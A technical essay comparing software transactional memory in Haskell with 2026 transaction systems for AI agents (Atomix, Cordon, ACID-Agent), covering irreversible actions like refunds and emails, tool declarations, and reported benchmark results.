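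Haskell has an escape hatch here too, `unsafeIOToSTM`. The compiler's documentation, quoted in the forum thread *Is unsafeIOToSTM ever safe?*, warns that STM may abort a transaction in the middle of the `IO` action without running the usual cleanup code. On a Haskell mailing list, John (2008) suggested that the action must be safe to repeat, and safe to perform with wrong arguments even when it shouldn't happen at all, neither of which is true of a refund.

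The cost of ignoring the ban is easy to estimate. Suppose every attempt performs the action and then fails with probability 0.2, independently of the others. The average number of actions per commit is:

```
1 + 0.2 + 0.2² + 0.2³ + ...  =  1 / (1 − 0.2)  =  1.25
```

If the action is a $100 refund, a thousand completed tasks would pay out about $125,000 instead of $100,000, because one task in five would issue the refund at least twice.

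### Four ways to live with real actions

Forbidding irrevocable actions inside a transaction is the safest option. The transaction can return a list of refunds, which the program makes after the commit. This suits Haskell, where most code is pure. The 2008 version of *Composable Memory Transactions* points out that programmers in mainstream languages would have to duplicate library functions for use inside transactions and convert data between two formats.

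The system can also postpone an action until the commit. A joke package on Hackage offers `launchMissilesSTM :: STM ()`, which launches only one salvo, however many times the block reruns. It returns `()`, so the block gets no result from the launch. In the mailing-list thread *SimonPJ and Tim Harris explain STM*, one example launches the missiles and uses the result to decide whether to retry. That launch cannot be postponed, because the block needs the result before it can commit. A crash between the commit and the postponed action can also leave records of a refund that never happened.

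Compensation means performing an action immediately and undoing it if the transaction fails. The block gets a real result, but other people can see the action in the meantime, and the undo may fail. A company can try to reclaim a refund, for example, but the customer may already have spent it. Some actions, such as sending an email or launching a missile, can't be undone at all.

In 2008, Welc, Saha and Adl-Tabatabai proposed letting one transaction at a time become irrevocable. Any transaction that conflicts with it must yield, so the irrevocable one can take real actions and use their results. However, it can no longer be rolled back, and any other transaction that needs to take such actions must wait, even if it uses unrelated data. This suits short blocks of code better than agents, which may spend half a minute on a task and then fail for reasons other than a conflict.

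### What agent systems hold back

Three systems from 2026 bring transactions to agents. *Atomix* (Mohammadi, Potamitis and colleagues, 2026) combines postponement with compensation. In the paper's example, an agent reserves a hotel, a flight and a car, then emails a confirmation. Atomix makes the reservations immediately because it can cancel them, and gives the agent the real booking confirmations. It holds back the email and tells the agent only that the email is queued.

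When the agent has finished this phase, the software that runs it seals the transaction, so no more actions can join. Atomix then waits for earlier work on the same resources. Each transaction `T` has a number `e(T)` that gives its place in the order. Each resource `r` has a marker called a frontier, which moves up to a number only when every lower-numbered transaction that touches `r` has finished. The rule is:

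```
commit T only if  frontier(r) ≥ e(T)  for every r that T read or changed
```

Atomix next checks whether another transaction has changed anything that `T` read. If so, it aborts `T` and schedules a retry; otherwise, it sends the email. If the flight reservation had failed, Atomix would have discarded the email and cancelled the other reservations.

*Cordon* (Chen, Dong and colleagues, 2026) treats a whole task as one transaction. File changes go into a shadow copy that only the agent can read, and messages go into an outbox. Cordon also records which results the agent derived from which. Suppose an agent reads logs that contain a secret key, summarizes them, and drafts a message to colleagues. Each step is routine, but the record connects the secret to the message. Cordon checks such connections against the user's permissions and policy before it saves the files and sends the message.

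*Agentic Transaction* (Sun, Wang and Li, 2026) presents ACID-Agent, a data-analysis agent named after the four classic guarantees of database transactions. In each cycle, the agent explores the data with read-only code, runs an analysis and checks it. A small model estimates how likely the agent's code is with and without the evidence from the exploration. If the evidence makes little difference, the code may not be based on the data. The agent retries after that result, an error or a poor review by a language model, up to twice per cycle in the tests. Files and conversation from failed attempts don't carry over, but the agent gets feedback on what went wrong.

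### What the tools have to declare

Atomix needs an adapter of about 17 lines for each tool. The adapter specifies which resources a call touches, whether the runtime can undo or delay its effect, and how to recognize a repeated request. The tool stays the same, but every call has to go through the adapter.

Atomix relies on the adapter's declarations being correct, as an MCP client does when it acts on `readOnlyHint`. Mohammadi and colleagues deliberately introduced mistakes into these declarations and ran 200 trials of each kind. Adapters that listed too few resources led to 66 broken data rules, and adapters that declared the wrong kind of effect let 17 irreversible actions escape. Listing too many resources only reduced how much work could run at once.

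Cordon requires each tool to declare its reads, writes, external effects and need for approval. It either rejects tools whose effects can't be declared or records their calls as violations. It relies less on declarations for shell commands. It runs each command on a copy of the working directory, with the network blocked by default, and then checks for changed files. In one test case, a routine-looking helper command tried to add data to a file that controls remote logins, and Cordon detected the write without having to interpret the command.

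The tests of ACID-Agent placed few demands on tools, because the agent mostly wrote code that analysed files. Sun and colleagues propose ready-made skills with built-in logging and compensation for actions outside the workspace, but they didn't test irreversible external actions.

### How well the systems worked

Mohammadi and colleagues tested whether a workflow would send an email after something had gone wrong. They used five causes, such as a failed tool or outdated data, and ran each 100 times:

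| Method | Emails sent by mistake, out of 500 |
|---|---|
| Atomix | 0 |
| Separate try, confirm and cancel steps for each tool | 0 |
| Restore a checkpoint and replay | 200 |
| Compensation | 400 |
| No transactions | 500 |
| Atomix with the email tool mislabelled | 300 |

Every method also delivered all 500 emails that it should have sent. For any given cause, each method either failed every time or never did, so the totals depend on which causes the researchers chose and don't predict how often mistakes would happen in practice. The test does confirm that compensation can't replace holding an email back. Separate try, confirm and cancel steps worked as well as Atomix but took about 50 lines of code per tool.

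Atomix has less of an advantage in recovering from ordinary failures. On 30 simulated retail tasks where each tool call had a 30% chance of failing, GPT-4.1 finished 57% cleanly with Atomix and 53% by restoring a checkpoint and replaying the work, a statistical tie. Six other methods scored between 0% and 7%.

Atomix did better at preventing conflicts between agents. When four simulated agents worked on the same order, locking it separately for each call allowed about five conflicting changes per run, because the order was unlocked while an agent planned its next step. Atomix allowed none in 100 runs. Holding a lock for the whole task was equally safe but made agents wait 112 milliseconds on average.

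Chen and colleagues built 45 risky workflows, including mass deletions and messages derived from secrets. An unprotected agent completed the forbidden action in all 45. Adapted versions of existing defenses stopped 14 in time, and Cordon stopped all 45. The researchers designed these cases around risks that appear only across several steps, so the perfect score shows that Cordon works on the kind of risk it was built to catch. It didn't seem to hinder ordinary work. On samples from two standard benchmarks, the agent scored 90.0% with Cordon and 87.5% without it on one, and 100% both ways on the other.

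Cordon also undid failed work more completely than Git, the usual tool for restoring earlier versions of code. After each of 15 scripted failures, Cordon restored the files well enough for work to continue. Git's ordinary reset failed all 15 times because it left new files behind. With an added cleanup command, Git succeeded 12 times, but it still missed changed file permissions.

On KramaBench, a set of 104 data-analysis tasks, ACID-Agent scored 74.6% and Claude Code scored 64.0% with the same model, Qwen3.5. With a stronger model, GLM-5.2, the gap shrank to about three points. The two agents differ in many ways, so a narrower comparison is better evidence about transactions. When Sun and colleagues let failed attempts affect ACID-Agent's files and memory, its score on environmental tasks fell from 90.0% to 78.3%. Some of that drop may be chance, since scores on these tasks vary from run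 to run, but the result suggests that discarding failed work improves the agent's reasoning as well as protecting its files.

### Where agents differ from memory transactions

STM reruns a block with the same code on newer data, but a language model may take different actions on a retry even if nothing has changed. Claude Code's scores on the environmental tasks typically varied by about 31 points between runs of the same task.

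Request identifiers are a weaker defense against duplicates when an agent can change its request on a retry. Suppose an agent refunds $100 but never gets the reply. When it retries, it rereads the returns policy and decides on $90. If the identifier depends on the amount, the service treats the two attempts as separate requests and refunds $190 in total. If the identifier depends only on the step, the service may return the result of the first refund, and the agent may report $90 when the customer received $100.

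STM can check everything a block read because all changes to shared variables go through STM. But Atomix's version counter for an invoice goes up only when a transaction commits through Atomix. If the customer pays on the billing website, the counter stays the same, and Atomix may release a reminder for an invoice that has already been paid. Some services give each record a version number and accept a change only if the number still matches. This check protects the invoice from an outdated change, but it doesn't stop an email based on the old invoice.

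Agents also leave much more time for such changes. Chen and colleagues' workflows took about 25 seconds each without Cordon. If an invoice changes at random once every ten minutes on average, it will change during about 4% of tasks that long. Even if the system detects the change, the rerun requires more model calls, and by then the invoice may have changed again.

Postponed actions are awkward for agents because the model uses each result to decide what to do next. A dry run has to invent a result for the same reason. An agent that is told only that a refund is queued can't give the customer a refund number or respond if the service later rejects the refund. The holiday example avoids this problem because the email comes last and nothing depends on its result. If a task needs the result of an irreversible action halfway through, the developer can split the task into two transactions, but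 a failure in the second then no longer rolls back the first. Two emails held until the end of a task can also cause trouble, because the second may fail after Atomix has sent the first.

### The rule that still holds

For agents as for STM, code that may run again should contain only actions that the system can discard or undo, or that are harmless to repeat. Types can express this rule. In a system like ELBA, where the agent writes a Haskell program, a developer could define a type for work that may run again:

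```
find_invoice :: InvoiceId -> Attempt Invoice
save_draft   :: Text -> Attempt ()
refund       :: InvoiceId -> Amount -> IO RefundNumber
run          :: Attempt a -> IO a
```

If an agent's program must have the type `Attempt`, it can look up invoices and save drafts to a staging area, but a program that calls `refund` won't compile. The program can return a proposed refund as data. Trusted code outside the attempt then makes the refund and handles any lost reply without sending the decision back to the model. Atomix and Cordon apply their labels at run time. Sun and colleagues list typed tool interfaces among the open problems.

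The developer still has to decide which tools belong in `Attempt`. `find_invoice` adds a log line and may mark an invoice as viewed, and a failed attempt undoes neither. By John's two tests, the developer can include `find_invoice` if an extra lookup does no harm and nobody relies on the viewed mark, even when the agent looks up the wrong invoice.
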